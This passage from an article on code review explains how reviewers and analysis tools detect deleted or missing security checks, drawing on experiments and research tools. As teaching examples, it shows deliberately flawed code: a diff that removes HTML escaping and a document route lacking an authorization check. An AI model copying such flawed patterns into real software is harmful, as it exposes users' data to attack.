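odds with an instruction = 84 / 33 ≈ 2.55

odds without = 8 / 25 = 0.32

odds ratio = 2.55 / 0.32 ≈ 8

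At least one flaw was found by 72% of instructed reviewers and 24% of uninstructed reviewers, a ratio of about three. Each reviewer had two flaws to find. When each flaw is counted separately, uninstructed reviewers found 8 of 66 (12%) and instructed reviewers found 127 of 234 (54%), which is about 4.5 times the rate and gives an odds ratio of 8.6.

Even a threefold increase is large for an instruction of a couple of sentences. The evidence is also stronger than that for the gain after the warning in the holiday experiment, because here a comparison group reviewed the code without the instruction.

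Still, each participant did only one review, right after reading the instruction. If the same instruction appeared at the top of every pull request, it might lose its effect as people got used to it. Of the 522 people who opened the experiment, 357 did not finish. If the instruction led people with little interest in security to drop out, the results would overstate its effect.

### Why the checklists made no clear difference

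The two checklist groups did about as well as the group given only the instruction. But the checklists could still have a useful effect that didn't show in these results because of chance. For the MD5 flaw, the seven-item list could plausibly have lowered the detection rate by 13 percentage points or raised it by 28.

Of the 76 people who had a checklist, 32 said it helped. One had overlooked the data going into the log until an item on the list prompted them to check it. Others had found a flaw before they consulted the list, and a few ignored the list or read it only after finishing the review. People who missed the MD5 flaw despite having a checklist mostly said they lacked the knowledge. One of them had considered the algorithm and judged it a good choice. A checklist can prompt a reviewer to examine the hashing, but it doesn't help much if they then judge a weak algorithm acceptable.

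Both flaws were also visible in the code. The name "MD5" appeared in a line of its own, and the line that built the log message included the database command. Someone told to look for security problems could find both by reading each line more suspiciously. The experiment therefore doesn't test whether a checklist helps with a missing check, where every line may look fine.

A checklist may be more useful for finding a missing check. An item such as "Does every route that returns a document check the user's team?" gives the reviewer a reason to expect the check, which the diff for the export route does not. A general instruction to look for security problems does not give that reason either, and a general warning helped few people in the holiday experiment find the unchecked quantity. But a reviewer could still read the item, assume that the check is somewhere else, and tick the box.

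An experiment on ordinary bugs gave mixed results. In *Do explicit review strategies improve code review performance?*, Wurzel Gonçalves, Fregnan and colleagues (2022) hired 70 developers from an outsourcing company, most with little or no experience of review. The developers reviewed one small change and two larger ones with no aid, with an 18-item checklist, or with a guided version of it. The guided version took them through the change one class and method at a time and showed only the items relevant to each.

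People with the guided checklist found more defects in the small change, while people with the ordinary checklist found more in one of the two larger changes. Participants found few of the defects whichever aid they had, and Wurzel Gonçalves and colleagues did not find a strong relationship between guidance and performance. This is weak support for checklists, and it comes from mostly novice reviewers looking for functional bugs.

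### Giving one reviewer the job of finding omissions

Older experiments tested a more demanding aid, in which each reviewer follows a set procedure to look for one class of fault. Some of these reviewers had to look specifically for what was missing. They read requirements documents, which are written before the program and describe what it must do.

In *Comparing Detection Methods For Software Requirements Inspections*, Porter and Votta report results from 48 graduate students and then from 18 professional developers at Lucent Technologies. Teams of three inspected specifications for a car's cruise control and a water-level monitoring system. The researchers knew of 26 faults in one document and 42 in the other, all of them real mistakes rather than planted ones. Team members read alone for up to two hours, then met to combine their findings.

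Some teams had only a list of fault types, divided into omissions and incorrect or ambiguous statements. Others also had a checklist of questions drawn from industrial checklists. In the remaining teams, each member followed a different procedure. One looked for inconsistent data types, another for incorrect functions and the third for missing or ambiguous functions. Averaging Porter and Votta's results for individual inspections gives these detection rates:

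| Method | Students | Professionals |
|---|---|---|
| List of fault types only | 37% (13 inspections) | 25% (4 inspections) |
| Checklist | 33% (8 inspections) | 16% (4 inspections) |
| A different procedure for each member | 51% (11 inspections) | 38% (4 inspections) |

Teams with assigned procedures found the most faults in both groups. The professional figures come from only six teams, but they are more believable because they agree with the larger student experiment. Checklists did no better than the list of fault types, and among the professionals they did significantly worse.

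Porter and Votta estimated that the three procedures together covered only about half of the faults that the checklist addressed. In these experiments, teams with the narrower assignments still found more faults overall. But the team totals don't separate the faults a reviewer was asked to find from the others, so they can't show how much the assignment helped the person looking for missing functions.

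The method also changed two things at once, by giving reviewers a procedure to follow and dividing the work among them. A reviewer working alone can use the procedure but can't divide the work. Teams that used the procedures in one round also had to use them in the next, so that what they had learned wouldn't carry over to the other methods. If those teams happened to be better, the comparison would favour the procedures.

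The most useful idea to carry over to code is giving one reviewer a narrow question about omissions. If two people review the export feature, one could check whether the export works while the other checks only who should be refused and which line of code enforces that. Someone working alone could read the change twice, once for each question. Both suggestions are extrapolated from documents of 24 and 31 pages that described a whole system. A diff leaves out most of the system, so the reviewer looking for omissions would also need time to read other files.

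### A reading procedure for one pull request

These steps turn the same idea into a procedure for changes like those to the document application. The procedure is a proposal, and the evidence for its parts is uneven:

| Step | Basis |
|---|---|
| Write down the expected checks before opening the diff | Reasoned advice |
| Read the deleted lines first | Reasoned advice, with indirect support from research on file order |
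| For each deleted or loosened condition, find out what now does its job | Reasoned advice |
| Compare each new route with similar ones | Reasoned advice |
| Ask for refactoring in a separate pull request | One experiment, which found fewer false alarms but no more defects |

Skilled reviewers don't normally work through a fixed list. *Code Review Comprehension* (2025) observed people whom others had recommended as great reviewers and found that they read opportunistically, taking up whatever seemed useful for understanding the change. The study didn't test whether they miss fewer omissions this way. A reviewer could keep reading like this and use the steps to check that they have covered everything before approving.

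#### Before opening the diff

Suppose that the pull request has the title "Add PDF export for documents". Before looking at the code, the reviewer writes down what the feature ought to refuse or clean:

- It should refuse anyone who isn't in the team that owns the document.
- It should refuse a document number that doesn't exist.
- If the PDF builder treats any text as commands, the route should escape titles and contents first.

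The reviewer then opens the diff and writes a file and line number beside each item. No line in the export route deals with the team, so the first item stays blank. This blank makes the omission visible, even though nothing in the diff looks unusual. A check in another file may still protect the route, so the reviewer searches the other files for one.

The order matters because tidy code can shape what a reader expects. A reviewer who reads the export route first may, like the people in the card experiment by Cherubini and colleagues, give too much weight to what is there and judge only whether its three lines work. Writing the list first should reduce that risk, but confirming this would require an experiment comparing reviewers who write the list before reading the code with reviewers who write it afterward.

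The list depends on what the reviewer knows. Someone who doesn't know that documents belong to teams won't write the first item. The project can help by stating its rules briefly in the repository, such as "Only members of a document's team may read it, in any format." Whoever writes the feature can use these rules too. In Farinha's tests, models produced more secure code when given written security requirements.

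Reviewers should take the purpose of a change from the original request where there is one, because a pull request's description can repeat the author's mistake. They should also keep their list of questions short, since three or four will cover most routes: who may do this, to which objects, with what values, and where the output goes. For the holiday program, the question about values would lead a reviewer to consider zero, a very large number and a negative number.

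#### Deleted lines first

Next, the reviewer looks at everything the change removes. The version-control program Git can print only the deleted lines, here for a branch named `cleanup`:

```text
git diff main...cleanup | grep '^-'
```

The output also includes a few header lines with file names. It omits the context, so it is useful for spotting removed conditions but not for judging them.

Research on file order gives this step some indirect support. GitHub and similar tools list changed files alphabetically, so a file's name can determine when people read it. Fregnan, Braz and Çalikli (2022), in *First Come First Served*, moved two planted defects between the first and last files of a change. Participants had 64% lower odds of finding one type of defect when its file came last. For example, if 50% found it in the first file, about 26% would find it in the last. Position made no difference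 for the other type.

In real projects the pattern is weaker. *Does Order Matter?* (Rahman, Codabux and Roy, 2026) examined 330,343 pull requests that changed several files. Of the files in first position, 56.7% were later part of a bug fix, compared with 61.5% of those in thirtieth position. Alphabetical order may also separate different kinds of files, so position may not cause even this small difference. Each extra file in a pull request lowered any one file's odds of getting a comment by about 8.7%. But files that got comments were no less likely to need a fix later, so comments aren't a good measure of whether anyone checked a file properly.

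These studies suggest that reviewers should read risky code early, but they don't show that deletions are the right place to start. The reason to start with deletions is that a removed check is one of the few omissions visible in a diff, and looking for one takes little time if the change deletes only a few lines.

Another experiment suggests that changing the reading order needn't do harm. *A Systematic Literature Review and Taxonomy of Modern Code Review* (2021) describes an experiment that compared people who read the tests first with people who read the production code first. The test-first group found more defects in the tests and the same proportion of defects in the production code as the other group.

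#### Finding out what replaced a condition

For every deleted condition, the reviewer asks which users it blocked and what blocks them now. For example, the change that moved the document lookup into a shared function also dropped the team condition. Searching the repository for `team_id` would show whether any other code still compares the document's team with the user's. The reviewer should also look at anything that runs before the route, such as a central permission check.

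There are three satisfactory outcomes:

- The condition has moved, and the author or reviewer can point to its new line.
- It was redundant, because another line already refuses the same people.
- The company no longer wants the rule, and someone with the authority to drop it has said so.

An answer of "it's handled elsewhere" must include the location. The reviewer should then open that code and confirm that requests to this route pass through it, because a function that compares teams offers no protection if the route never calls it.

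The reviewer has to ask this about each deleted line separately. In the Debian case, only one of the two identical OpenSSL lines was safe to remove.

A loosened condition needs a slightly different test. The reviewer tries to think of a user who would fail the old check but pass the new one. When `current_user.is_logged_in` replaces the comparison of teams, any logged-in user from another team is an example. The reviewer can then ask whether that user should be able to read the document, which is easier to answer than whether the new condition looks reasonable. A product manager could also answer that question without reading code.

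This works for changes that don't touch the condition itself. If a pull request alters the function that looks up a user's team, the reviewer can search for the conditions that use its result and ask the same question about each.

#### New routes and their neighbours

A new route leaves no deleted condition for the reviewer to investigate, so the reviewer needs something to compare it with. For the export route, the reviewer can use other routes that take a document's number, such as those for viewing, renaming or deleting a document. The reviewer opens two or three and notes what each does before it returns or changes anything. The viewing route compares teams but the export route doesn't, and the new feature doesn't explain the difference.

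Similarity in purpose is more useful here than similarity in the code. A route that exports a public price list might look almost identical to the document export but still be a bad guide, because anyone may read a price list. The reviewer should choose routes that handle the same records.

Neighbouring routes can also be missing a check they need. If the routes for renaming and deleting documents also lack the team condition, a central check may protect all of them, or several people may have made the same mistake. The reviewer has to look for the central check to know which. Programs can automate some of the comparison between routes, but a reviewer who already knows the application can often do it by opening one file.

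Having found a difference, the reviewer should write it down straight away. In Porter and Votta's experiments, the professionals' team meetings uncovered new faults amounting to 5.0% of the total but lost 6.7% that individual members had already found. They may have forgotten those faults or let others talk them out of reporting them. A written comment avoids some of that loss. For the export route it could read:

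> This route returns any document to anyone who requests it. `show_document` rejects requests from users outside the document's team. Please add the same check here, or point to the code that already applies it.

The comment identifies the unchecked path, the rule and a likely fix, and makes it easy for the author to correct the reviewer if the check exists.

#### Refactoring in a separate pull request

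Before they start reading, reviewers can ask for restructuring and new features to be in separate pull requests. If a pull request only restructures code, every check in the old version should still apply in the new one. If a condition that checks the user's team disappears, the reviewer can object without knowing why documents belong to teams, because the author has said that the program's behaviour stays the same. When the same pull request also adds a feature, the missing condition is harder to judge because the author may have changed the rule on purpose.

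That argument rests on logic, and the experimental evidence supports only part of it. In *The effects of change decomposition on code review* (2018), di Biase, Bruntink and colleagues asked 28 developers and students to review changes to a small Java game. The changes moved a method into a parent class and added behaviour for one of the player's enemies. Half of the participants saw the changes in one pull request, and the other half saw them split across two. The code contained three planted functional defects, so each group of 14 had 42 chances to find one.

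| | One pull request | Two pull requests |
|---|---|---|
| Defects found | 20 of 42 | 17 of 42 |
| False alarms | 6 | 1 |
| Median review time | 831 seconds | 759 seconds |

Only the difference in false alarms was statistically significant. In one false alarm, a reviewer of the combined change complained that only one class used a method, when other classes in the hierarchy also used it. People who reviewed the changes separately also looked for context more often, which a reviewer needs to do to find a condition that has moved.

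The experiment found no evidence that separating refactoring helps people find more defects, although with 14 people in each group it could have missed a moderate benefit. None of the planted defects was a lost security check, and the change was only about 100 lines. The effect might differ in a pull request with hundreds of deleted lines. For now, the best-supported reason to separate refactoring is that authors will have fewer mistaken comments to answer.

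### Time, false alarms and unread checklists

Small additions to review take up a lot of time in a large organisation. In OWASP's example, if a company's 5,000 developers each spend an extra 15 minutes a week on a new task, the company uses 1,250 hours a week, roughly the work of 30 full-time people. OWASP adds that this may still be worthwhile compared with finding the bug later, when the company would have to investigate and fix it, release a new version and deal with customers.

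In the password experiment, people who took longer to review the code were more likely to find the revealing log message, and those who had been interrupted for longer were less likely to. Careful people may simply take longer, so this doesn't show that making someone spend another ten minutes would help. A developer whom Braz and Bacchelli interviewed described losing attention when there was a lot of code to review, and losing track of how the system fits together after interruptions.

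Teams can limit the extra work by using the full procedure only where a missing check would matter. OWASP warns against spending as much time on a three-line change to a web page's styling as on a redesign of the login code. Teams should decide based on what the code does, not on the pull request's title. A reasonable rule would be to use the procedure whenever a change adds a route, changes a condition that denies someone access, or handles external data in a new way.

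It is less clear how many false alarms an instruction produces. *Less is More* gives no count of mistaken reports, and everyone in the experiment reviewed code with two real flaws. The instructed reviewers may have raised more unfounded objections as well as more correct ones. The evidence on checklists is mixed. Braz and colleagues cite one student experiment in which checklist users had half as many false positives as those without one, and other studies that found no significant difference in performance.

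The usefulness of looking for missing checks depends largely on how often a check that seems to be missing turns out to exist in another file. Searching for it before commenting takes the reviewer's time but saves the author's. The project can save both of them time on later pull requests by recording which routes a central check covers.

People can also complete a checklist without reading the code, even when the software prompts or forces them to answer every item. In the password experiment, the software warned participants about unanswered items, yet some still gave the list little attention. The guided checklist in the experiment by Wurzel Gonçalves and colleagues went further by requiring people to mark each item before continuing.

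A checklist item is harder to complete without looking at the code if it asks for a location. A colleague can verify "Team condition: `documents.py`, line 41" in a few seconds, whereas "Authorization checked" shows only that someone ticked a box. The reviewer of the export route would have had no line number to enter.

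## Tools that point to a removed or missing check

Programs can do part of the repetitive work of accounting for deleted conditions and comparing neighbouring routes. Static analysis tools can detect some missing checks from evidence in the code, but they can detect others only if someone supplies the rule that the application should enforce.

### Omissions that leave a trail

Suppose that a change simplifies how a page shows a document's title:

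```diff
-    title = html.escape(doc.title)
-    return "<h1>" + title + "</h1>"
+    return "<h1>" + doc.title + "</h1>"
```

A tool can find the missing `html.escape` call by tracing data. Its rules list sources (places where outside data enters the program), sinks (operations that are dangerous if the data contains commands) and functions that make the data safe. Here the source is a title typed by a user, the sink is the page sent to the browser, and `html.escape` used to make the title safe before it reached the page. Without that call, the tool can trace the title from source to sink and report the path. It would report the same path in new code that never had the escaping.

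This works because unescaped text is dangerous in every web application, so the tool's makers can list the sinks in advance. The export route also has a flow, from the document number in the request to the document in the reply. But every correct route has such a flow too, so a tool that reported them all would flag the whole application.

Tools can detect some cases of missing input validation but not others. They can trace a file name from outside the program to a function that opens files. In the holiday program, however, the number of days reaches a subtraction, which no general-purpose tool treats as dangerous.

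Liu, He and colleagues (2026), in *Repairing Broken Access Control in Web Applications with LLMs*, give a definition that shows what the tool lacks. Let P be the intended policy, which answers "allow" or "deny" for every possible request q, and let P_impl be the answer that the code actually gives. The application has an access-control flaw if any request belongs to this set:

{ q : P(q) = deny and P_impl(q) = allow }

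A tool can infer P_impl from the code, at least roughly, but it can't read P because, as Liu and colleagues point out, hardly anyone documents the policy.

Most tools look for flaws that leave traces in the code. In *Many Tools, Few Exploitable Vulnerabilities*, Hermann, Peldszus and Berger (2026) reviewed 246 static security analysers from the research literature and found that most target a small set of well-known weaknesses, such as injection and memory errors. Semgrep and CodeQL, another widely used analyser, found none of the 30 disclosed access-control flaws that Duarte and colleagues collected.

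To find missing authorization, a tool needs a substitute for P. It can use the previous version of the same code, on the assumption that whatever the old version refused, the new one should refuse too. Or it can use the rest of the application, on the assumption that similar routes should enforce similar rules. (Newer tools ask a language model to work out the policy.)

### Comparing a change with the version before it

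The crudest comparison needs only a list of the words that a project's security checks contain. This command prints the added and deleted lines that mention a team, a refusal or escaping:

```text
git diff main...cleanup | grep -E '^[-+].*(team_id|abort\(403\)|escape\()'
```

For the refactoring in which an agent moved the document lookup into a shared function, it prints:

```diff
-    if doc.team_id != current_user.team_id:
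-        abort(403)
```

If the condition had moved to the shared function, the output would also include matching plus lines. For the change that loosened the condition to allow any logged-in user, the command prints only the old condition, which is enough to prompt a question. It prints nothing for the export route, because the route is new and there is no old version to indicate what it should refuse.

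A list of words also misses any check written in an unexpected way. In *SCAFFOLD-CEGIS*, Chen, Bian and colleagues (2026) built a more thorough version for code that a language model revises repeatedly, where checks can disappear without anyone reading each diff.

### Listing the elements that must survive

Before each revision, SCAFFOLD-CEGIS makes a list of security-critical elements, which the paper calls anchors. It looks for them in three ways.

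The tool searches for functions whose names begin with words like `validate`, `sanitize` and `auth`. Because a name may not show what a function does, the tool also starts from dangerous operations, such as running a database command or opening a file, and traces the data back towards the user's input. Any function along the way that handles this data and either contains a condition or raises an error becomes a candidate check. This can find a function called `isSafePath`, which the name search would miss.

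It also matches common forms of defensive code, such as a line that raises Python's `PermissionError` or a database query that keeps values separate from the command. Finally, it applies general rules for the type of task, such as the rule that every path to a sensitive operation must pass a permission check.

The team condition in the document application would be easy to miss because it sits inside the route rather than in a function with a descriptive name. It also denies access with `abort(403)`, so a project would probably have to add that form to the list. Only the general rules could catch the export route, because they can apply to code that never had a check, but someone has to write them and state which operations are sensitive.

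Each new version then has to pass four tests, or gates:

- The program's own tests must pass.
- Semgrep must report no more serious problems than it did for the previous version.
- The numbers of added and deleted lines must stay within a limit.
- The listed elements must still be there.

The system rejects the version if the most important elements are missing. For less important losses, it either has the model try again or only issues a warning. After a rejection, the system sends the model an explanation of what it broke, and the model tries again. If it runs out of attempts, the old version stays. The model can also request to move an element, and the system then checks that the new code covers everything the old code did.

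Some of the last gate's checks are plain text searches, which can confirm that a line is still in the file but not that requests still go through it. The system also relaxes its protection of an element if versions that break it are repeatedly accepted in the end. This reduces false alarms but could leave a security check unprotected.

### Security loss over ten AI edits

To measure the problem, Chen, Bian and colleagues took 24 short Python and Java programs that already had their defences and tests in place, and asked GPT-4o to revise each one ten times in a row. They ran four sequences per program, which asked for new features, better performance, stronger security or vague improvements. After ten rounds, 43.7% of the 96 sequences had more Semgrep findings than at the start. Even among those that asked for stronger security, the paper gives a figure of 28.6%. (The breakdown by type of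 request needs some caution. The four rates average 41%, and none of them corresponds to a whole number out of 24.)

In tests with three other models that counted only serious findings, between 4.2% and 10.5% of sequences ended up worse. All of these models are now old.

Semgrep can't see most lost checks, so the researchers added a second measure. They had Claude Opus 4.5 read the first and last versions in each sequence and count security problems that scanners tend to overlook, such as missing defensive code. They call an increase in these problems latent security degradation. These are the results for GPT-5-Nano with different safeguards:

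| Safeguard on each edit | Sequences with more serious Semgrep findings | Sequences with more latent problems |
|---|---|---|
| None | 11.5% | 12.5% |
| Security advice in the prompt | 9.4% | 10.4% |
| The model criticises and rewrites its own work | 11.5% | 10.4% |
| Reject edits that add Semgrep findings | 0% | 20.8% |
| Reject edits that fail the tests | 10.4% | 22.9% |
| Both of those gates | 0% | 12.5% |
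| SCAFFOLD-CEGIS | 0% | 2.1% |

The zeros in the middle column are expected because those safeguards reject any edit that would raise the count. The right-hand column is more informative because it shows that a project relying on Semgrep alone would have seen no increase in the count even though a fifth of its sequences lost protection.

Chen, Bian and colleagues argue that the Semgrep gate made things worse, perhaps because the model treated a clean scan as proof of safety and attempted bolder changes. The evidence for that is weak. The percentages fit 96 sequences per safeguard, which would mean 20 with the gate and 12 without, and that difference could easily be chance. The drop from 12 to 2 with the full system is harder to attribute to chance, although the sequences all start from the same 24 programs and so aren't fully independent.

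The paper describes three losses that its researchers confirmed by hand. A model deleted a function called `validate_user_input` when asked to simplify the code. The database queries were still safe from injection, so neither Semgrep nor CodeQL reported anything. When asked to improve performance, a model replaced specific error handling with a block that silently discards errors. When asked for an administrator shortcut, it added a path that skipped the permission check. The system caught all three using its list of elements. The shortcut is the same kind of flaw as the export route.

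The overall rates, though, depend on a language model's ability to notice missing code, which Fox and colleagues found models do poorly. If the model misses the same share of problems for every safeguard, the ranking of safeguards should still hold, but the true rates could be higher.

It is also unclear how much of the improvement comes from the list of elements. The limit on the size of changes and the explanations after each rejection may also have helped. The researchers tested versions of the system with parts switched off, but reported only Semgrep findings for those versions, not latent problems.

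The full system rejected 39% of the model's attempts, including those that failed the tests, and completed 77% of the requested revisions. When the system explained its rejections, the model went on to repair 53% of the rejected attempts, up from 23% without explanations. All the programs were single files of under 400 lines, so the system's performance on a large application is unknown.

### Clearing a warning by deleting the code

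Comparing versions also guards against an agent removing a defect by deleting the code that contains it. A tool that only looks for defects would report that deletion as a success.

Wynter (2026), in *Fixed or Deleted?*, measured how often this happens. The study planted 31 defects in 25 pull requests to well-known open-source projects and had three of Anthropic's models repair each pull request five times, which makes 125 runs per model. Working alone, the agents had instructions to review the change and fix any problems it introduced. In other runs, they received findings from CodeAssure, a commercial checker that reports where a change breaks a project's rules. The checker can also notice when a file that the pull request added has disappeared, and tell the agent. These are the numbers of runs in which the agent removed the feature:

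| Model | Alone | With findings, deletion check off | With findings, deletion check on |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 13 | 19 | 7 |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | 31 | 29 | 2 |
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 44 | 17 | 0 |

The largest model deleted the feature most often when it worked alone, in 44 of 125 runs. The findings by themselves didn't reliably prevent this, but the deletion check nearly eliminated it. Most of the agents that would have deleted the feature repaired it instead.

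Wynter's company makes CodeAssure, so it has an obvious interest in these results. Wynter discloses this and has published the outcome of every run, but the agents' changes are available only under a confidentiality agreement. The study also concerns deleted features, not deleted security checks. The planted defects were breaches of project rules, such as console output in the wrong place or a forbidden import between parts of a program, so its figures don't measure how often agents delete an authorization check to clear a warning.

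After the main scoring, Wynter inspected the repairs more closely and found 21 in Python where the agent had kept the file but removed what the pull request had added to it. The agent had deleted a validator, which got rid of a forbidden import the validator needed, but no other code performed the same check. Eight of the 21 happened with the deletion check on, because it looks only for missing or emptied files. Wynter recommends extending it to functions and validators, which would bring it close to the list of elements in SCAFFOLD-CEGIS.

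For a reviewer, this is another reason to read the deleted lines first when a pull request's purpose is to clear a tool's warnings.

### Inferring a rule from the rest of the code

If a check was never written, no earlier version of the code contains it, so a tool has to compare the code with similar code instead. Engler, Chen and colleagues set out this approach in 2001 in *Bugs as Deviant Behavior*. They wanted to find errors in operating systems whose rules nobody had written down, and reasoned that they could infer the programmers' beliefs from the code.

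A tool can sometimes find a missing check by looking for two pieces of code that contradict each other. For example, the kernel, the core of an operating system, must not directly use a memory address supplied by an ordinary program, because the address could point anywhere. It has to use special functions that check the address first. If a driver passes an address to one of these functions, its programmer evidently thinks the address is untrusted. If the same driver also uses that address directly, one of the two uses must be wrong, and the tool can report this without knowing where the address came from.

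This approach found 35 security holes in Linux and OpenBSD. In the two versions for which Engler and colleagues counted false alarms, it found 30 holes and raised 19 false alarms.

The same tool compared functions that play the same role. For example, many Linux drivers supply their own "write" function. Of the 57 the tool compared, 55 treated a particular address as untrusted and two used it directly. Both of those were real errors. A reviewer does much the same when comparing the export route with the viewing route, but with fewer examples to compare.

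Often the code only departs from a habit, without contradicting itself outright. If most of the code that returns a document compares teams first, that may reflect a rule or a coincidence. Engler and colleagues treat every such habit as a possible rule, count how often the code follows it, and rank the exceptions from most to least suspicious.

### Ranking the exceptions

The ranking uses a standard statistic for comparing proportions. Let n be the number of places where a possible rule applies and e the number that follow it. The paper assumes that by default about 90% of places would follow it, so p₀ = 0.9:

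z = (e/n − p₀) / √(p₀(1 − p₀)/n)

The numerator is how far the share of cases that follow the rule exceeds the expected 90%. The denominator is how much that share would typically vary by chance in a sample of that size. The larger z is, the more likely the rule is real and the exceptions are mistakes.

Suppose that 20 routes return a document and 19 of them compare teams first:

z = (0.95 − 0.9) / √(0.09/20) = 0.05 / 0.067 ≈ 0.75

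If there are 200 such routes and 199 compare teams:

z = (0.995 − 0.9) / √(0.09/200) = 0.095 / 0.021 ≈ 4.5

There is one unguarded route in each case, but the one in the larger application ranks much higher. Both the share and the number of examples matter, as these invented cases show:

| Similar routes | Routes with the check | Share | z |
|---|---|---|---|
| 6 | 5 | 83% | −0.5 |
| 10 | 9 | 90% | 0 |
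| 20 | 19 | 95% | 0.75 |
| 200 | 190 | 95% | 2.4 |
| 200 | 199 | 99.5% | 4.5 |

The score only ranks reports. It isn't the probability that a route is vulnerable, and the 90% figure is a convention. Serious flaws in a small application can rank low, because one unguarded route out of six gets a negative score however serious the flaw is. A reviewer who can open all six routes doesn't need the score.

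Engler and colleagues list "does this security check protect that operation?" among the rules that the method could infer, but they report results only for other rules. One of those is that code should check whether a function succeeded before using its result. In Linux and OpenBSD, they found 195 places where this check was missing and had 37 false alarms. These figures somewhat overstate the method's accuracy, because the researchers read the reports from the top of the ranking and stopped when too many were wrong.

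### Finding missing authorization in Linux

*AutoISES*, by Tan, Zhang and colleagues, applies the idea directly to authorization. Linux has functions that decide whether a program may do something, such as read a file, and kernel programmers have to call the right one before each sensitive operation. In one old version, the ordinary functions for reading and writing files did this, but a less common one, `readv`, skipped the check, as the export route did. Users could therefore read files they had no permission to open.

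It is hard for a tool to recognise that `read` and `readv` do the same thing, because their code looks different. AutoISES compares the data they access. Given a list of the authorization functions, it collects the data that the program usually accesses after calling each one. For reading and writing files, it collected 22 items, such as a file's size and settings. It then looks for other code that accesses the same data without calling the function first.

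AutoISES inferred 84 rules in Linux and Xen, a program for running virtual machines. It divided exceptions to these rules into errors, where an untrusted program could reach the unguarded operation, and warnings, where it apparently could not. Six of the eight errors were real. The researchers read the 28 most suspicious of the 293 warnings and found two more real problems. Five of the eight real problems could be exploited. The other three were inconsistencies, such as code that skipped the usual authorization function and called the underlying one directly.

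One of the two false errors occurred because the check was elsewhere. The code that collects the results of a file operation had no authorization check, but a program must submit the operation first, and the check happens then. However, if someone withdrew the user's permission between the two steps, the operation would still go through. Linux developers agreed that this was possible but were unlikely to change it.

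AutoISES confirms that the code calls an authorization function, but not that the function examines the right object. It would not flag a route that checked the user's access to one document and then returned another. It also relies on programmers not trying to defeat it, so someone who wanted to hide an omission could add a meaningless call.

### Web applications without standard checks

AutoISES needs a list of authorization functions, which web applications often lack. One application may compare team numbers, while another looks up a role in a database or reads a setting from the login session. *RoleCast* (Son, McKinley and Shmatikov, 2011) looks for missing checks "when you do not know what checks are", in the words of its title. Rules also differ between roles within an application. An administrator's page needs a different condition from an ordinary user's, so comparing the two would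 only produce false alarms. RoleCast therefore tries to work out which conditions guard sensitive operations for each role, then looks for code in that role that lacks them.

*Chucky* (Yamaguchi, Wressnegger and colleagues, 2013) is meant to help people who audit code by hand. The auditor picks a function that handles something sensitive. Chucky finds similar functions, notes which conditions each one applies to the same data, and reports any condition that the chosen function lacks. It scores each missing condition by the share of similar functions that have it. If nine of the ten functions most like `export_document` mention `team_id` in a condition and `export_document` doesn't, the missing condition scores 90%. The auditor learns which function looks odd and which condition it lacks, and can put both into a review comment. The same method can point to missing input validation, which the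 AutoISES approach doesn't cover.

MACE, a later research tool for web applications, compares authorization across the places where an application changes the same data. It also checks whether the code limits the change to the current user's own records. That makes it suitable for cases like the loosened team condition, where a simpler tool would treat the remaining login check as protection.

These tools differ mainly in how they define similar code. AutoISES and MACE compare code that uses the same data, RoleCast compares code that has the same role, and Chucky compares functions of the same kind.

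### Two ways the majority misleads

All of these tools treat the usual practice as the rule, which fails when that practice is wrong. If the export route's neighbours also lack the team condition, none of the routes is an exception and the tool reports nothing. By the formula above, 0 of 20 routes gives z ≈ −13, which puts the possible rule at the bottom of the list.

Programmers can spread a mistake by copying code. Engler and colleagues found one mistake that had been copied into 20 places and another that had been copied into five drivers. A coding agent that bases a new route on existing ones could spread a missing check in the same way. If an agent wrote the whole application from scratch, there may never have been a correct route to compare with.

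To find such a flaw, a tool needs a standard from outside the application. In *Finding Security Bugs in Web Applications*, Near and Jackson present Space, a tool that uses a catalogue of common access-control patterns. Someone states which kinds of data in the application correspond to those in the catalogue, and Space reports any access that no pattern allows. If the catalogue includes a pattern for data that belongs to one group, Space would report every unguarded route. *A Security Policy Oracle* compares separate implementations of the same software, since a permission check missing throughout one may still appear in another. Few companies have a second implementation of their own application, so the catalogue is more practical for most of them.

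The opposite failure is an exception that someone intended. Say that the company lets users publish a document by creating a secret link:

```python
@app.get("/shared/<token>")
def show_shared(token):
    doc = Document.find_by_share_token(token)
    return page(doc)
```

This route correctly returns a document without comparing teams, because anyone with the link may read the document. If the other 199 routes compare teams, the tool gives this one a score of 4.5, the same score it would give an export route that lacked the check by mistake. Refining the statistic cannot separate the two, because they differ in the policy P, not in the code. The reviewer has to ask whether the company meant to allow this access.

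### Running a tool on one pull request

These tools were designed to search whole programs, so a reviewer who runs one on an established project may get hundreds of reports about code that the pull request doesn't touch. The following suggestions for narrowing down the reports are based on reasoning, because none of the studies tested its tool on individual pull requests in review.

The reviewer can run the tool on the code before and after the change and read only the differences in its output. A report that appears only in the second run probably concerns the change. The comparison also covers indirect effects, such as a change to a shared function that removes protection from routes elsewhere.

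However, the tool should infer its rules from the old version of the code, because a large pull request can add enough exceptions to hide an existing rule. Suppose that an application has 20 routes that all compare teams, and an agent's pull request adds ten that don't. If the tool uses the old code, all ten are exceptions to a rule that every route followed. If it uses the new code, only 20 of 30 routes compare teams, z falls to about −4, and the ten reports move to the bottom of the list.

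The tool should read the list of security-critical elements from the main branch, and nobody should be able to change that list in a pull request unnoticed. Otherwise, someone could delete a check and its entry on the list in the same change and get a clean report.

The reviewer then follows up each report as they would a deleted condition or a difference between neighbouring routes. The tool saves time by identifying the route and the condition, and it can search more files than a person would, but it can't determine whether the route needs the condition.

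The checker's list is also incomplete. In one of Wynter's pull requests, a change had broken four calls to a function, but the checker reported only one. In four of five runs with the checker, the smallest model fixed only the reported call, although it had fixed all four in every run without the checker. A human reviewer might also stop after dealing with the only warning.

### What false alarms cost

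False alarms about missing authorization take longer to dismiss than most. Tan and colleagues note that people can usually confirm a buffer overflow quickly once a tool points to it. To dismiss a report of a missing check, they have to show that the operation isn't sensitive or that another check covers it, and this can require knowing how other programs use the code.

The AutoISES results give some idea of how long it takes to check a tool's reports. If each report took 15 minutes to settle (an invented figure), the eight errors would take two hours and yield six real problems, or 20 minutes per problem. The 28 warnings the researchers checked would take seven hours and yield two, or three and a half hours per problem. The remaining 265 warnings would probably take longer per problem, since the researchers started with the most suspicious. Whether three and a half hours is too long depends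 on what the flaw would expose.

A team could show a tool's most reliable reports on every pull request and leave the rest for an occasional audit. Engler and colleagues worked through their ranked reports in a similar way and gave up on a rule once it produced mostly false alarms. The threshold should probably be stricter in code review, because the same people see the tool's comments every day and may stop reading them.

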